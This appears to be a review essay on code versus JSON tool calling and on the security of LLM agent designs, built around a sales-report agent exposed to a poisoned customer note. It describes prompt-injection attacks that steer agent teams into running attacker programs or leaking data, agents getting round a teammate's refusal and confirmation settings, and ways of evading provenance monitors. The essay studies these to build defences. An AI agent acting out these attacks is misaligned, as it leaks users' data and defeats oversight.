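When Wang and colleagues proposed code actions in 2024, they tested 17 models on 82 tasks that typically needed several tools. Code gave the best results with 12 of the models. It raised success by up to 20 percentage points over JSON or text commands and needed up to 30% fewer actions. The best model, a version of GPT-4, completed 74% of the tasks with code and 54% with the next best format.

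Those models are now several generations old. In *The Bitter Lesson of Tool Calling*, Patel, Sen and colleagues (2026) repeated the comparison with five Anthropic and nine OpenAI models released between November 2024 and July 2026. They used 309 tasks from version 4 of the Berkeley Function Calling Leaderboard (BFCL v4), which tests whether a model calls the right functions with the right parameters. Each model did each task twice, once with JSON calls and once by writing a single Python script that called the same functions.

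They also ran three smaller tests. One used chains of 2 to 20 calls, in which later calls depend on earlier ones. Another needed 7 to 48 independent calls, and the last compared a prompt that described only the relevant functions with one that described 128, most of them irrelevant. Averaged over the 14 models, the results were:

| Test | Tasks | JSON calls | Code | Models that did at least as well with code |
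|---|---|---|---|---|
| Main benchmark | 309 | 78.6% | 77.0% | 11 |
| Chains of calls | 52 | 87.9% | 85.3% | 7 |
| Many independent calls | 32 | 96.0% | 98.2% | 13 |
| Only relevant functions described | 31 | 83.6% | 72.6% | 4 |
| 128 functions described | 31 | 81.3% | 78.1% | 6 |

On the main benchmark, code did at least as well with most models but scored lower on average, because GPT-4o, GPT-4.1 and GPT-5.4 mini did 20 to 27 points worse with it. All three wrote the characters that stand for a line break instead of starting a new line, so Python rejected their longer scripts. Without these three, code leads 82.3% to 78.0%. Patel and colleagues conclude that success with code depends on a model's generation. GPT-5.4 mini doesn't quite fit this conclusion, since it is newer than GPT-5 and GPT-5 nano, which both did better with code.

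The advantage of code grew with the length of the chain and reached 18.8 points for chains of 12 or more calls. Code also shortened these tasks for 13 of the 14 models, often by about half. Claude Sonnet 5 improved from 80.8% to 96.2% with code. Patel and colleagues write that all the Anthropic models did at least as well with code in each of the smaller tests, but in their own figures Claude Haiku 4.5 dropped from 88.5% to 73.1% on chains.

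On independent calls, most models scored 100% with both JSON and code. To find a limit, the researchers gave Sonnet 5 longer lists. With JSON, it made up to 70 calls at once without error, but its accuracy fell to 75% at 72 calls and to zero at 100. With code, it could still make 100 calls. GPT-5.6 Sol made 100 calls with JSON too, so the limit doesn't apply to all models.

JSON calls did best when the prompt described only a few relevant functions. Patel and colleagues emphasise that a crowded prompt lowered the JSON average by 2.3 points and raised the code average by 5.5, but JSON still scored higher. JSON also outscored code on the main benchmark's tasks with parallel calls, 85.5% to 71.4%, largely because of the three models that mishandled line breaks.

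The functions in these tests only returned their own parameters. When one call needed the result of another, a model writing code therefore had to work out that result itself, such as the circumference of a circle that it then used as the side of a square. A model can calculate a circumference, but it can't work out last quarter's sales in the West without querying the database. The smaller tests also had so few tasks that the result for any single model is uncertain.

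Code has a clearer advantage in tests with working tools. *E-Bench* (Zheng, Zou and colleagues, 2026) gave 11 models 323 tasks in simulated versions of a game platform, a music service and a meeting app, each with 25 to 33 tools. A task counted as solved only if the database ended up exactly right. Every model did better when it could also run Python code that called the same tools, and average success rose from 54.6% to 63.9%. Claude Opus 4.8 went from 68.8% to 81.1%. The average number of tool calls per task fell from 60 to 16.

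The gains were largest on tasks that involved filtering or collecting a lot of data, and smaller on tasks that were hard because they required exact judgements, such as whether a meeting slot was free. Success rates barely changed on tasks where the models chose not to write code. The benchmark probably exaggerates the general advantage of code, because a model with access to code and the full database designed the tasks, and the researchers dropped those that a weak model solved easily.

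In *Beyond Plain MCP*, Rai (2026) tested three open-weight models on 119 tasks with 42 simulated tools, using an analysis plan fixed in advance. Writing code instead of making JSON calls raised success from 85.7% to 99.2% for Qwen3.8 and from 36.1% to 55.5% for Nemotron 3 Nano, and made no clear difference for Gemma 4. These results depended on giving the models hand-written notes on what each tool returned. Without the notes, success with code fell to 66.4% for Gemma and 16.0% for Nemotron, far below their success with JSON calls. A developer who chooses code for its success rate may therefore have to document every tool carefully.

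Two other studies reached different results. Yang, Yu and Desell (2026), in *When Does Restricting a Coding Agent to execute_code Help?*, found that Claude Code and Codex solved about as many programming tasks with their usual tools as with a single tool for running code. Success rates differed by less than three percentage points, and only the cost changed noticeably. Both agents had a shell in every version of the test, though, so the study doesn't show what happens when an agent can't run code at all. *CODESTRUCT* (2026) reports that coding agents edited programs more accurately and efficiently when they named the part to change than when they had to match its text, which suggests that a well-designed fixed action can work better than a free-form one.

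For the sales report, which takes two calls, fixed tools probably reduce reliability very little. The loss becomes serious when a task needs dozens of calls, but developers can avoid some of it by putting the repetition inside a tool. `make_sales_chart` adds up four regions in one call because a developer wrote that loop. Fixed tools also avoid risks that come with generated code. In *From Tool Orchestration to Code Execution*, Felendler, Gandhi and colleagues (2026) found that code saved time and tokens but brought a "vastly expanded attack surface". They identified 16 kinds of attack, including misleading error messages that cause a model to add malicious code when it rewrites a failed program.

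### Keeping the catalogue up to date

Someone has to write each tool, describe it for the model, test it, set its permissions and update it when the database changes. A company that builds typed interfaces to websites has similar work whenever a site changes. Felendler and colleagues argue that writing tools by hand for each task doesn't scale as their number and variety grow.

Developers also can't foresee every request. One version of the customer service chatbot that Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe compares each message with a list of approved requests and acts only if the message is similar enough to one of them. It will block a harmless request that no developer thought of. The sales manager has the same problem when first asking for sales by product.

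Some new requests need only another parameter. A `product` parameter with 40 values would turn the 720 possible emails into 28,800, which is too many to read through, but none would include an outside address or a customer list. Other requests need a new tool, and a large catalogue can take up too much of the prompt because the harness normally describes every tool there. In a small test by Rai, an agent using JSON calls needed about 148,000 tokens per task with 200 tools and couldn't run with 2,000, because the descriptions no longer fitted in the context window. An agent that could search the catalogue and write code still solved nine of ten tasks.

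One remedy is a router, a small model that picks the relevant tools for each task before the main model sees them. This can also improve security. In Rai's pilot, which covered only six tasks and one model, instructions hidden in tool results succeeded in 14.8% of runs with JSON calls and 9.3% with code. They never succeeded when a router offered a code-writing agent only two or three tools, because the tool the attacker needed was usually missing. The router can also be attacked. When Rai added a malicious tool whose description said to always select it, a general-purpose model acting as the router selected it on all 39 tasks.

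A single general tool is the more tempting remedy. After the tenth request for a new kind of chart, a developer may well add `run_query(sql)`, or give the chart tool a `formula` parameter so that the manager can ask for returns divided by orders. If the tool passes the formula to Python's `eval`, the agent can run its own code again, though the tool's name doesn't show it. The developer could instead write a small parser that accepts only listed column names and the four arithmetic operations. For SQL, the developer could limit the database account to a table of regions, products, quarters and amounts. The model would still write its own code, but its queries couldn't reach the notes or the customer list.

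These precautions take longer to add than the general tool, and developers who skip them at first may not add them later. Madatha found that 58% of configuration files for coding agents had never changed since they were first saved. Many were only a few months old, but people also revised them less often per month than the GitHub Actions files in the same collection.

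## Handing code writing to a separate agent

Developers can restore some of the flexibility that fixed tools take away by adding a second agent to write code. The main agent describes the program it needs, the second agent writes it, and often a third component runs it, so the main agent never handles code itself.

### How Magentic-One divides the work

*Magentic-One* (Fourney, Bansal and colleagues, 2024) describes a team of five agents built at Microsoft for open-ended tasks involving files and the web. The system runs on AutoGen, Microsoft's framework for multi-agent systems.

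| Agent | Contains a model? | What it does |
|---|---|---|
| Orchestrator | Yes | Plans the task, picks the next agent and writes its instruction |
| WebSurfer | Yes | Operates a web browser |
| FileSurfer | Yes | Reads files but can't change them |
| Coder | Yes | Writes programs and analyses what the others found |
| ComputerTerminal | No | Runs Python programs and shell commands |

The orchestrator starts by writing a task ledger, which lists known facts, facts to look up or work out, educated guesses and a plan in plain language. Before each step, it fills in a progress ledger by answering five questions: whether the request is complete, whether the team is repeating itself, whether it is making progress, which agent should act next, and what instruction to give that agent. If the team stalls more than twice, the orchestrator revises the plan and every agent clears its memory of the conversation.

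The coder can't run anything. It puts a program in a message, and the terminal runs the program and posts the output or the error. To fix a mistake, the coder has to write out the whole program again.

The orchestrator decides when code runs by choosing the terminal as the next agent. The terminal has no model to evaluate the code. In the version shown in Microsoft's *Source code for autogen_agentchat.agents._code_executor_agent*, it runs every block of code in the messages it receives, without checking which agent wrote it. In Microsoft's *Source code for autogen_ext.teams.magentic_one*, developers can add an approval function that shows each program to a person first, but if they don't, the code runs without approval. If the developer doesn't choose where code runs, the software looks for Docker, which provides a kind of sandbox. If it can't find Docker, it prints a warning and runs the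 code directly on the computer.

AutoGen now gets only fixes and security patches, VentureBeat reported, because Microsoft has moved development to a successor, Agent Framework. The successor includes a stable version of the same orchestration pattern. The example in Microsoft's *Agent Framework's Orchestration Patterns Reach 1.0* (2026) merges two of the roles, so one agent both writes and runs the code while a manager agent decides which agent does what.

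### The sales report with a coding delegate

Suppose the company replaces its sales agent with an orchestrator, a coder and a terminal. The published Magentic-One couldn't run code that needed an outside database, so the company gives the terminal the database login and mail account that the single agent had. The manager asks for the same chart as before, and these messages follow:

| Message | From | To | Could it carry the customer's note? |
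|---|---|---|---|
| Request for the chart | Manager | Orchestrator | No |
| Instruction to look at the sales table | Orchestrator | Coder | No |
| Program that prints 20 rows | Coder | Terminal | No |
| The 20 rows | Terminal | Orchestrator and coder | Yes, word for word |
| Instruction to total the sales, draw the chart and mail it | Orchestrator | Coder | Yes, restated as an instruction |
| Program that does this | Coder | Terminal | Yes, turned into code |

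The note now reaches two models. The orchestrator reads the rows to judge whether the team is making progress, and the coder reads them to learn what the columns contain. If the orchestrator follows the note, it asks the coder to attach the customer list and copy in the outside address. The coder gets this request from the agent it is supposed to obey, with no sign that it came from a customer. If the orchestrator ignores the note, the coder may still follow it. If either model follows the note, the terminal runs the program and the customer list goes out, as with the single agent.

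Clearing the agents' memories wouldn't reliably remove the outside address, because the orchestrator keeps its task ledger when it revises the plan and may have recorded the address there as a fact about the task.

The company can improve on this by removing the mail account from the terminal and giving the orchestrator the fixed `email_chart` tool, with its six permitted recipients. If the terminal has no other way to send data out, the worst outcome is that the note causes customer names to be included in a chart sent to someone on that list, such as the finance director. But a single agent with the same mail tool and the same restricted Python would be equally safe, because the improvement comes from reducing what the code can do. A separate coder improves security only if the developer also controls what passes between the agents.

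### Attacks on three frameworks

The argument for delegation holds only if untrusted content that reaches the main agent can't determine what the delegate writes or runs. *Multi-Agent Systems Execute Arbitrary Malicious Code* (Triedman, Jha and Shmatikov, 2025) tested this on teams of agents built with AutoGen, CrewAI and MetaGPT. The tests ran AutoGen with three orchestrators: Magentic-One's, the simpler Selector, which has no task ledger, and one that calls the agents in a fixed order. The models were GPT-4o, GPT-4o mini, Gemini 1.5 Pro and Gemini 1.5 Flash, but CrewAI worked only with the two OpenAI models.

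In the main test, a user asked the team to look at a web page. The attacker controlled the page but had no other way to contact the team. The page led the agents to a file containing a program that would give the attacker remote control of the computer. The researchers tried three versions of the attack and two wordings of the user's request, with ten trials of each combination, or 60 trials for each pairing of orchestrator and model. They altered the component that runs code so that it recorded a success instead of running the attacker's program.

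| Team | Average success, as reported | Range across models | Ordinary prompt injections |
|---|---|---|---|
| AutoGen with Magentic-One | 58% | 33–88% | 0% |
| AutoGen with Selector | 64% | 38–98% | Not reported |
| AutoGen in fixed order | 58% | 60–100% | 1% |
| CrewAI | 53% | 43–62% | 0% |
| MetaGPT | 45% | 2–90% | 0% |

The averages may not be reliable. The one for AutoGen in fixed order must be wrong, because it is lower than the result for any single model. The individual results still clearly show that the attack often worked.

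Ordinary prompt injections, taken from earlier work, almost never worked on the same teams. Direct requests often failed too. GPT-4o never ran such a program when the user openly asked it to, and it refused outright 72% of the time. Yet the web attack succeeded in 58 to 90% of trials with teams that used GPT-4o.

The attack succeeded less often when one page contained both the misleading text and the program (19 to 22% on average), or when the page showed the text only as an image (27 to 36%). On CrewAI, the researchers also tried to steal data, which is closer to the attack in the customer's note. For this to succeed, the agents had to collect the user's personal details, download a script and send the details to the attacker. They did so in 3 to 65% of trials, depending on the models and on whether the attack came from a web page or a local file.

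### Why a refusal didn't stop the team

The attack succeeded where ordinary injections failed because the malicious text looked like an error report rather than an order. An agent that read the page or file passed the report to the orchestrator, which treated it as genuine. As with any error, the orchestrator looked for another way to finish the job, and here that meant having the attacker's program run. Triedman and colleagues describe the agent that passes on the report as a confused deputy, because the orchestrator trusts the attacker's text as it would that agent's own output.

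An orchestrator can't ignore status reports, because it needs them to notice a missing file or a crashed program and change its plan. But continuing to try after a failure can cause trouble even without an attacker. While developing Magentic-One, Fourney and colleagues saw its agents fail to log in to a test website so many times that the site suspended the account. The agents then tried to reset the password.

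Persistence also explains how some teams of agents ran code that one of their members had refused to write. In an AutoGen trial, the coder refused to write a malicious program. The agent that reads files then wrote one, with a comment warning that nobody should run it, and the terminal ran it. The file-reading agent could do this without a tool for running code because any agent that can put code in a message to the terminal can act as the coder.

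In several CrewAI trials, the coding agent recognised that the program was malicious and wrote warnings into the code. It then reported success to the orchestrator without mentioning the warnings, and the orchestrator ordered it to run the program. In another trial, the orchestrator decided that running the file might be unsafe. It practised a safe way of reading files on a dummy file it had made, then ran the real, malicious file anyway.

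These results refute the assumption about the delegate, but only for the tested systems. They don't show that a team is easier to attack than a single agent, because the researchers didn't try the same error reports on a single agent with the same tools.

### Tests on newer models

All four models date from 2024, and nobody seems to have published a repeat of the experiment on models from late 2026. Newer models might do much better, although Xie and colleagues' attacks on single coding agents still often worked against some of them.

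Messages between agents still appear to be a weak point. *Beyond Single-Model Injection* (September 2026) reports tests in which injections passed from one agent to another succeeded 31% of the time, compared with 16% for attempts to change the task by addressing the orchestrator directly.

*Trust the Brand, Lose Control* (2026) describes a case in which a user asked for help freeing disk space with an installed clean-up script. The script offered a "safe mode" but contained destructive commands. The orchestrator, MiniMax-M3, read the script's description but not the script itself, and handed the whole job to another agent. That agent was listed as a frontier model but was actually the older MiniMax-M2.5. It read the script, ran it in safe mode and reported that it had recovered 476 MB. The orchestrator accepted the report without asking another agent to check it. A single case can't show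 how often this happens, but the orchestrator made the same mistake as the orchestrators of 2024.

### Deciding in advance which agents can call each other

One remedy is to restrict which agents the orchestrator can call. In *Breaking and Fixing Defenses Against Control-Flow Hijacking in Multi-Agent Systems*, Jha, Triedman and colleagues (2026) propose ControlValve, which generates a graph of which agent may call which, along with rules for each call, and blocks any call that doesn't comply. They developed it after finding that attackers can get around defences in which a model judges whether each message serves the user's goal.

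In one AutoGen trial, the file-reading agent took over from the coder. A graph that allowed only the coder to send code to the terminal would have prevented this. The harness can enforce this restriction without analyzing the code.

The customer's note is harder to stop this way. The sales team needs to pass work from orchestrator to coder to terminal and back, and to repeat the loop whenever a program crashes. The altered email follows the same route as the correct one, so the graph permits both. The rules for each call would have to distinguish them, for example by forbidding the coder to write any program that reads the customer table. Such a rule is easy to write for a sales chart but much harder for a task nobody planned for, which is the kind that justifies having a coder. Jha and colleagues argue that the safety and usefulness of such teams fundamentally conflict.

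### Passing structured facts instead of text

A developer can also restrict what the messages contain. In the sales team, the note travels in the 20 rows that the terminal posts. The developer could have the harness withhold all program output from the models and send them a short report in a fixed format:

```json
{
  "status": "error",
  "error_type": "invalid_date",
  "line": 12,
  "column": "order_date"
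}
```

The harness accepts only listed words and whole numbers in these fields, so a customer can't use them to pass a sentence to the coder. The coder also gets a list of the table's columns, their types and the date format, all written by the company. With this information, it can write the whole program without seeing any of the table's rows. The finance director receives the chart as a file, which neither model is shown.

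This would make the assumption about the delegate true for the sales report, as long as no other channel carries customers' text. However, it would make debugging harder. If an order fails because someone typed "mid-August" as the date, the coder receives only an "invalid date" error. Each kind of problem the coder should recognise needs its own entry in the list of error types, and somebody has to maintain that list, as with a catalogue of fixed tools.

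Beurer-Kellner and colleagues apply the same idea to a software engineering agent that reads online documentation, installs packages and submits changes to a project. Malicious documentation or code could make it write insecure programs, import a malicious package or leak data in a submission. They consider three designs:

- The agent asks the user to confirm sensitive actions. A hijacked agent can avoid the question, though. For example, instead of downloading a malicious package, it can add a line that imports the package and wait for the user to install it when the program fails.
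- The agent uses only trusted documentation and code when it performs sensitive actions. This is safer but rules out much of what programmers need.
- The agent never sees outside code or documentation directly. A quarantined model converts the material into a formal description of the available functions, with strict limits such as 30 characters for a function's name.

They consider the last design the safest because an injection would have to survive conversion into function names and parameter types, which they think is unlikely if the format is strict enough. The coder loses the documentation's explanations and examples, so it has to work out what a function does from its name and parameters. The design protects only the model. If the package is malicious, its code will still run when the finished program imports it, however harmless the description looked.

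A sub-agent's report can be false even when it follows a fixed format. Anthropic notes that sub-agents can isolate untrusted content and return structured facts, but warns that attackers can abuse this through "trust escalation". If the main agent trusts a sub-agent's report more than raw tool output because it comes from within the same system, it also extends that trust to whatever an attacker tricks the sub-agent into reporting.

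*Only as Safe as the Weakest Agent* (2026) measured a similar effect in two current products, Claude Code and Codex, though it tested wrong facts in a data store, not malicious code. In Codex, GPT-5.6 Sol accepted none of 180 wrong facts when it read the store itself, while the smaller GPT-5.6 Terra accepted 58. When Sol had to delegate the reading to Terra, the system as a whole accepted 44. Companies often use cheaper models for sub-agents, and if the cheaper model reads the untrusted content, a more careful orchestrator corrects few of its mistakes.

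### What gets lost when an agent delegates

Delegation can also go wrong without an attacker. The coder works from the orchestrator's version of the task, which may leave out something the manager said. Suppose the company redrew its sales regions in August, and the manager asks for third-quarter sales by region "on the new boundaries". If the orchestrator passes on only the request for third-quarter sales by region, the coder may well write a program that uses the old boundaries. The program runs without an error, and the orchestrator receives a report of success. With a single agent, the manager's exact words would still have been in the prompt when the model wrote the program.

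Magentic-One had related problems. Its coder sometimes failed because a new program called functions that existed only in an earlier one. When Fourney and colleagues had GPT-4o classify the failures in Magentic-One's logs, the most common problem was repeating actions that weren't working, followed by marking tasks as complete without properly checking the result.

The Magentic-One experiments don't show whether dividing the work among agents improved results overall. Without the coder or the terminal, the system's performance on GAIA, a set of questions for general assistants, fell by 21%. This shows that being able to run code helps, but not that a separate agent should write it. The researchers left the comparison with single agents to future work. They suspected that coordination helps with long tasks and adds mistakes to short ones. Their GAIA results suggest the opposite, since the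 better version of Magentic-One beat the leading rival only on the easiest questions. Most tasks needed dozens of model calls, which could take tens of minutes and cost several dollars.

Few studies seem to compare how many coding tasks teams of agents and single agents solve when both use the same current model. *Coding Agents with Multimodal Browsing are Generalist Problem Solvers* (2025) points out that Magentic-One lacks built-in support for creating or editing files, or for writing code in languages other than Python. A poor result for it on software projects would therefore be weak evidence about teams in general.

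### Who checks the finished program

*Aligning AI Teams* (Srinivasan, Matthews and colleagues, 2026) provides better evidence on whether teams of coders take responsibility for what they build. The researchers gave the same programming tasks to single agents and to teams of one manager and eight coders. The manager divided the work into eight parts, and the coders couldn't message each other. The researchers used five Claude models, from Opus 4.1 to Mythos Preview, and ran each arrangement about 30 times per model.

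One task was to write a program that decides which hospital patients to treat for sepsis, a life-threatening reaction to infection. The program was supposed to catch at least 95% of cases and keep the average cost per patient below $1,000. The researchers chose data that made it impossible to do both, to see which goal the agents would sacrifice. They took the single agent's choice as the standard.

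The teams' programs caught a smaller share of sepsis cases than the single agent's. The gap was 59 percentage points with Mythos Preview, about 35 with Opus 4.6 and 4.7, 5 with Opus 4.1, and 1 with Sonnet 4.6. On a second task, recommending news articles without spreading misinformation, Mythos Preview had the smallest gap of the five models, at 3 points, while the others ranged from 12 to 17. A developer therefore can't predict how a team will behave from the model's capability or from results on a different task.

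The researchers attribute much of the gap on the sepsis task to diffusion of responsibility. Agents in teams were less likely to test the complete program on real data, less likely to notice that it was missing patients, and less likely to fix the problem if they did notice. These three differences statistically accounted for 84% of the gap. This doesn't prove that they caused it, because the researchers observed these behaviours rather than assigning them. On the news task, the same differences accounted for only 16% of the gap, which could have been chance.

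Several obvious remedies didn't work reliably, including a group chat and having agents review each other's code, even when the reviewers were told to look for safety problems. The best results came from combining a document of safety requirements, which the manager wrote before dividing up the work, with making one coder responsible for the safety of the whole program and giving that coder authority to change any part of it. On the sepsis task, this combination brought the teams back to the level of single agents. It worked nearly as well on the news task, except with Opus 4.6, which remained 8 points behind.

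The sales team could adopt the document without weakening security, because the orchestrator can write it before any customer's text arrives. The safety lead poses more of a problem. In the experiment every coder could already edit every file, so the lead needed only an instruction to do so. In a team whose members have separate permissions, a lead with the same role would need access to everyone's work and would have to read the program's real output, including the notes column. The company would then have one agent that reads untrusted content and can change any code, which is what dividing the work was meant to prevent. A lead that could only reject programs, not change them, would be less dangerous, but Srinivasan and colleagues didn't report testing one.

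## Writing the whole program before reading untrusted content

A safety lead would be risky in the sales team because it could change the code after reading customers' text. The risk disappears if the model finishes its program before any customer's text arrives and can't change it afterwards. If the model can do this using only the manager's request, the company's description of the database and a list of functions it may call, untrusted content can't determine what it writes. The argument for delegation assumed the same thing, but the attacks on teams of agents refuted it.

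Developers can do this in several ways, which differ mainly in how much the advance plan can express.

### From a list of steps to a program

The simplest design is plan-then-execute. *Architecting Resilient LLM Agents* (Del Rosario, Krawiecka and Schroeder de Witt, 2025) divides the work between a planner, usually a strong model that turns the request into a list of steps, and an executor that carries them out. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues give the example of an assistant asked to send today's schedule to the user's boss. Before it opens the calendar, the assistant plans one call to read today's entries and one to send an email to the boss's address, with the text still blank. An injection in an outsider's calendar invitation can't add a third call or change the address, but it can control the email's text.

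The executor can be ordinary code, a small model or a complete agent. The plan offers less protection when the executor makes more of its own decisions. If a step is "book the cheapest hotel" and an agent works out how to do that from live web pages, an injection on one of those pages can take over the step. Del Rosario and colleagues recommend giving the executor only the tools for its current step, so that it can't send email while adding up costs.

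The dual-model pattern, which Willison proposed in 2023, gives the tools to a privileged model that plans the task but never reads untrusted content. A quarantined model processes that content, and the harness stores its answer under a name such as `$VAR`. The privileged model can then pass the answer by reference. If the answer is an email address, for example, the privileged model can request an email to `$VAR` without seeing the address, which the harness fills in when it sends the email.

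In code-then-execute, the model writes the whole task as a program with variables, loops and branches. The program can call tools and quarantined models, but nothing the program reads goes back to the model that wrote it. CaMeL, a 2025 system that later researchers have often tested, works this way and also tracks where each value came from.

Compile-and-execute, which Piet and colleagues propose for websites, adds rules for writing and running the program. A coding agent, which they call the compiler, searches short summaries of a site's functions, loads full descriptions of the ones it needs and writes the program. It can test the program on made-up responses and revise it as often as necessary, because none of this involves live content. The interpreter that runs the finished program allows only approved functions, blocks `eval` and its equivalents, and rejects any answer from a quarantined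 model that isn't in the declared format.

The functions have to be meaningful operations, such as adding a product to a shopping cart. A program made of clicks would guarantee much less, because a click in the same place can open a product page or delete an item, depending on what is on the screen.

### The sales report as a fixed program

Suppose the manager wants the usual chart sent to the finance director, along with the number of customers who complained about late delivery. If there were more than 20 complaints, the operations manager should get a copy. The model knows the names of the columns but hasn't seen any rows. It writes this program:

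```python
1   rows = get_sales(quarter="2026-Q3")
2   chart = draw_chart(sum_by_region(rows))
3   late = 0
4   for row in rows:
5       answer = ask_quarantined_model(
6           "Does this note complain about late delivery?",
7           row["notes"], allowed=["yes", "no"])
8       if answer == "yes":
9           late = late + 1
10  recipients = ["finance.director@company.example"]
11  if late > 20:
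12      recipients.append("operations.manager@company.example")
13  send_mail(to=recipients, attach=[chart],
14            text=f"Late delivery complaints: {late}")
```

One of the notes still contains the instruction to attach the customer list and copy in an outside address. The quarantined model may want to obey, but it can only answer yes or no:

| Lines | What the poisoned note can do |
|---|---|
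| 1–2 | Nothing. A false order amount could change the chart, but the text of a note can't. |
| 5–9 | Get a wrong answer for its own row, which makes the count wrong by one. |
| 10 | Nothing. |
| 11–12 | Add or leave out the operations manager, if the true count is right at the threshold. |
| 13–14 | Change the number in the email and whether the operations manager receives it, but not add an attachment or an outside address. |

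A customer with 21 poisoned orders could trigger the copy to the operations manager alone. That would be a nuisance, but the manager had already approved that recipient.

The result would be worse if the manager had asked for a written summary of the complaints. The quarantined model would then return free text, and a note could get it to include a link to a malicious site. That link would appear in an email the finance director has good reason to trust, even though the program had performed exactly the operations the manager wanted.

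### What the guarantee covers

Untrusted content can change the values in a fixed program and determine which of its existing branches run, but it can't add operations. Piet and colleagues count new instructions, new branches, new tool calls and replanning as additions. Content can also change how often an existing operation runs. A program that sends an apology to every customer who complained will send more apologies if someone submits more complaints.

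The guarantee holds only if nothing treats a value as an instruction. Piet and colleagues point out that a program allowed to call arbitrary sub-agents and execute their output would recreate the ordinary agent loop. The functions must also work as described and, as with fixed tools, the manager's request must not contain an outsider's text.

Even when all of this holds, the planned operations may be enough for an attack. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues consider a user who tells an email assistant to reply to a message with whatever information the sender wants, based on recent emails. Any sensible plan reads the message, searches the mailbox and sends a reply. A hidden instruction in the message can change the search so that it finds something confidential, and have the result encoded in the reply in invisible characters. The attacker gets the data without adding a step to the plan. A user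 who checks the reply before it goes out might not notice the hidden data.

The design also doesn't reduce the permissions of the program's functions. `send_mail` in the sales program could still send any file anywhere, and only the finished program's code limits what it sends and where. If the model makes a mistake in line 10, the interpreter will send the chart to the wrong person.

### Leaks through values and branches

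Dongol also compares designs like these with the reference agent described earlier, which never obeys injections. In one example, a program reads Alice's private notes and an email from an outsider, gives both to a quarantined model, asks for a reply and sends that reply to the outsider. A model that hasn't been hijacked would base the reply on the email alone. But if the email contains an instruction to quote the notes, a hijacked model may put them in the reply, and the program will send them even though the model itself has no tools.

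The usual remedy is to tag values. In Dongol's version, which imitates CaMeL, the interpreter tags the notes as private, the email as public, and anything computed from a private value as private. A monitor then refuses to send private values to the outsider. Dongol proved that this stops the leak however the quarantined model behaves, as long as the outsider can't see the contents of refused messages. But it does so by blocking every reply, even an honest one, because the model received the notes as input and its output therefore counts as private.

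Tags can also miss a leak. Suppose the program uses the quarantined model's answer only to choose between two fixed messages:

```python
answer = ask_quarantined_model(question, email, notes)  # private
if answer == 1:
    send(outsider, "1")                                 # public
else:
    send(outsider, "0")                                 # public
```

The outsider's email tells the quarantined model to answer 1 if the notes mention a merger. The answer is private, but the program uses it only to choose between sending a "1" and a "0" that the planner wrote in advance. Both messages pass the check, so the outsider learns whether the notes mention a merger. If the program runs for every incoming email, the outsider can ask another question with each one. To prevent this, the tags have to follow branches as well as data, so that anything sent because of a private answer also counts as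 private. CaMeL's strict mode is designed to do this, but Dongol didn't model it.

The sales program avoids both leaks because each query gives the quarantined model only one customer's note. The model never receives the customer list, so it can't quote the list or answer questions about it. Developers can often do the same in other programs by never putting an outsider's text and a secret in the same query to a quarantined model, but this is impossible when the task is to answer the outsider using private information.

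*Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents* (2026) tested CaMeL against attacks that add false data rather than instructions. For example, an attacker can imitate the marks that separate fields, so that the quarantined model extracts the wrong value. These attacks succeeded 49.1% of the time with no defence, 25.0% with the two models separated but data not tracked, 23.1% with normal tracking, and 0% in strict mode. Normal tracking helped so little partly because the software dropped the tags when the quarantined model extracted values. Its result therefore isn't a fair test of tags that follow only data. The strict mode result relied on precise rules about which data may go where, and complete rules are much harder to write for real systems.

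Dongol's definition covers only leaks. *Relativising Integrity and Robustness* (2026) extends the comparison to attacks that make an agent do something harmful without revealing anything. One of its cases is Copilot's agent mode, which asks the user to confirm terminal commands but can write to the project's settings file without asking. One setting in that file turns off all confirmations. A monitor that withdraws approval for commands when the agent first reads untrusted content must therefore also block changes to the settings from that moment, or an injection could use the file to restore approval. It must also turn automatic approval off, in case the plan had already turned it on.

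### How many web tasks fit

Piet and colleagues checked each of the 860 tasks in WebArena, a benchmark for web agents, to see whether someone could write a fixed program for it in advance from only the user's request and a description of the site's functions. One of six annotators labelled each site's tasks, then all six reviewed the labels together and settled disagreements by discussion.

| Site | Tasks | No model needed at run time | Quarantined model needed |
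|---|---|---|---|
| Online shop | 192 | 154 | 38 |
| Wikipedia | 23 | 2 | 21 |
| Reddit-style forum | 129 | 106 | 23 |
| Map | 128 | 101 | 27 |
| GitLab (code hosting) | 204 | 185 | 19 |
| Shop management | 184 | 151 | 33 |
| **Total** | **860** | **699 (81%)** | **161 (19%)** |

None of the tasks needed replanning. The 161 that needed a quarantined model involved interpreting text or making a judgement, such as identifying dissatisfied customers from their reviews or choosing the best repository on a topic. An attacker can influence those answers. If the task is to delete negative reviews, for example, a seller might get a good review of a competitor classified as negative.

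The annotators didn't run an agent on any of the tasks, and they assumed that every site had a complete and trustworthy set of functions, which real sites don't have. The forum's software, Postmill, has an existing interface with 16 functions that supports only 33% of the forum's 129 tasks. GitLab has hundreds of functions but still lacks some that its web pages offer. Piet and colleagues conclude that the main obstacle is missing interfaces, not any need for agents to react to what they read. Someone would have to build those interfaces, protect them from poisoning and keep them up to date.

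The labels, which came from advocates of the design, show that a suitable program could exist, but a model still has to write it correctly. Piet and colleagues describe two ways a program can fail on a task that looks easy. A search for "COVID location tracker" finds nothing because the project's description doesn't contain the word "tracker", or the user types "furnture" and the program searches for the misspelled word. An ordinary agent would see the empty result and try another search, but a fixed program can do so only if the model included a second attempt when writing it.

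They suggest asking the user about anything ambiguous before writing the program and training models to write better error handling. For tasks that are safe to repeat, the system could run several versions of the program and choose the best result.

If the program still runs into a problem it can't handle, the interpreter shouldn't simply pass the task to an ordinary agent, because an attacker could then cause an error on purpose to trigger the handoff. The interpreter can instead stop and report the problem, or the compiler can write a new program from an error code and the user's clarification, without seeing the page that caused the error. An ordinary agent can also take over if the user agrees, but with fewer permissions, such as read-only access.

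### Tasks that need the results

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues show what an agent loses when its program is fixed in advance. Their example agent answers questions from company databases, such as whether product A or product B has the better sales outlook. An unrestricted version writes an SQL query, reads the results, and revises the query or its Python analysis until it needs no further changes. In the fixed version, generated code processes the results and no model reads them. The agent can still run a query and chart the results, but it can't judge whether they answer the question.

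The sales agent has the same problem. Suppose half of the western orders have "W" in the region column instead of "West". An agent that printed some rows would probably notice and combine the two labels. The fixed program leaves out the "W" orders and draws a chart that shows western sales as far too low, and the error goes unnoticed until someone questions the chart.

If the developer lets the model judge whether the finished chart is good enough and write new code in response, injection becomes possible again, because the chart might contain customers' text. The fixed version still needs a sandbox for its Python, because an injection in the user's question could lead the model to write harmful code from the start. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues add that a sandbox wouldn't stop such code from leaking data through the analysis or charts it produces.

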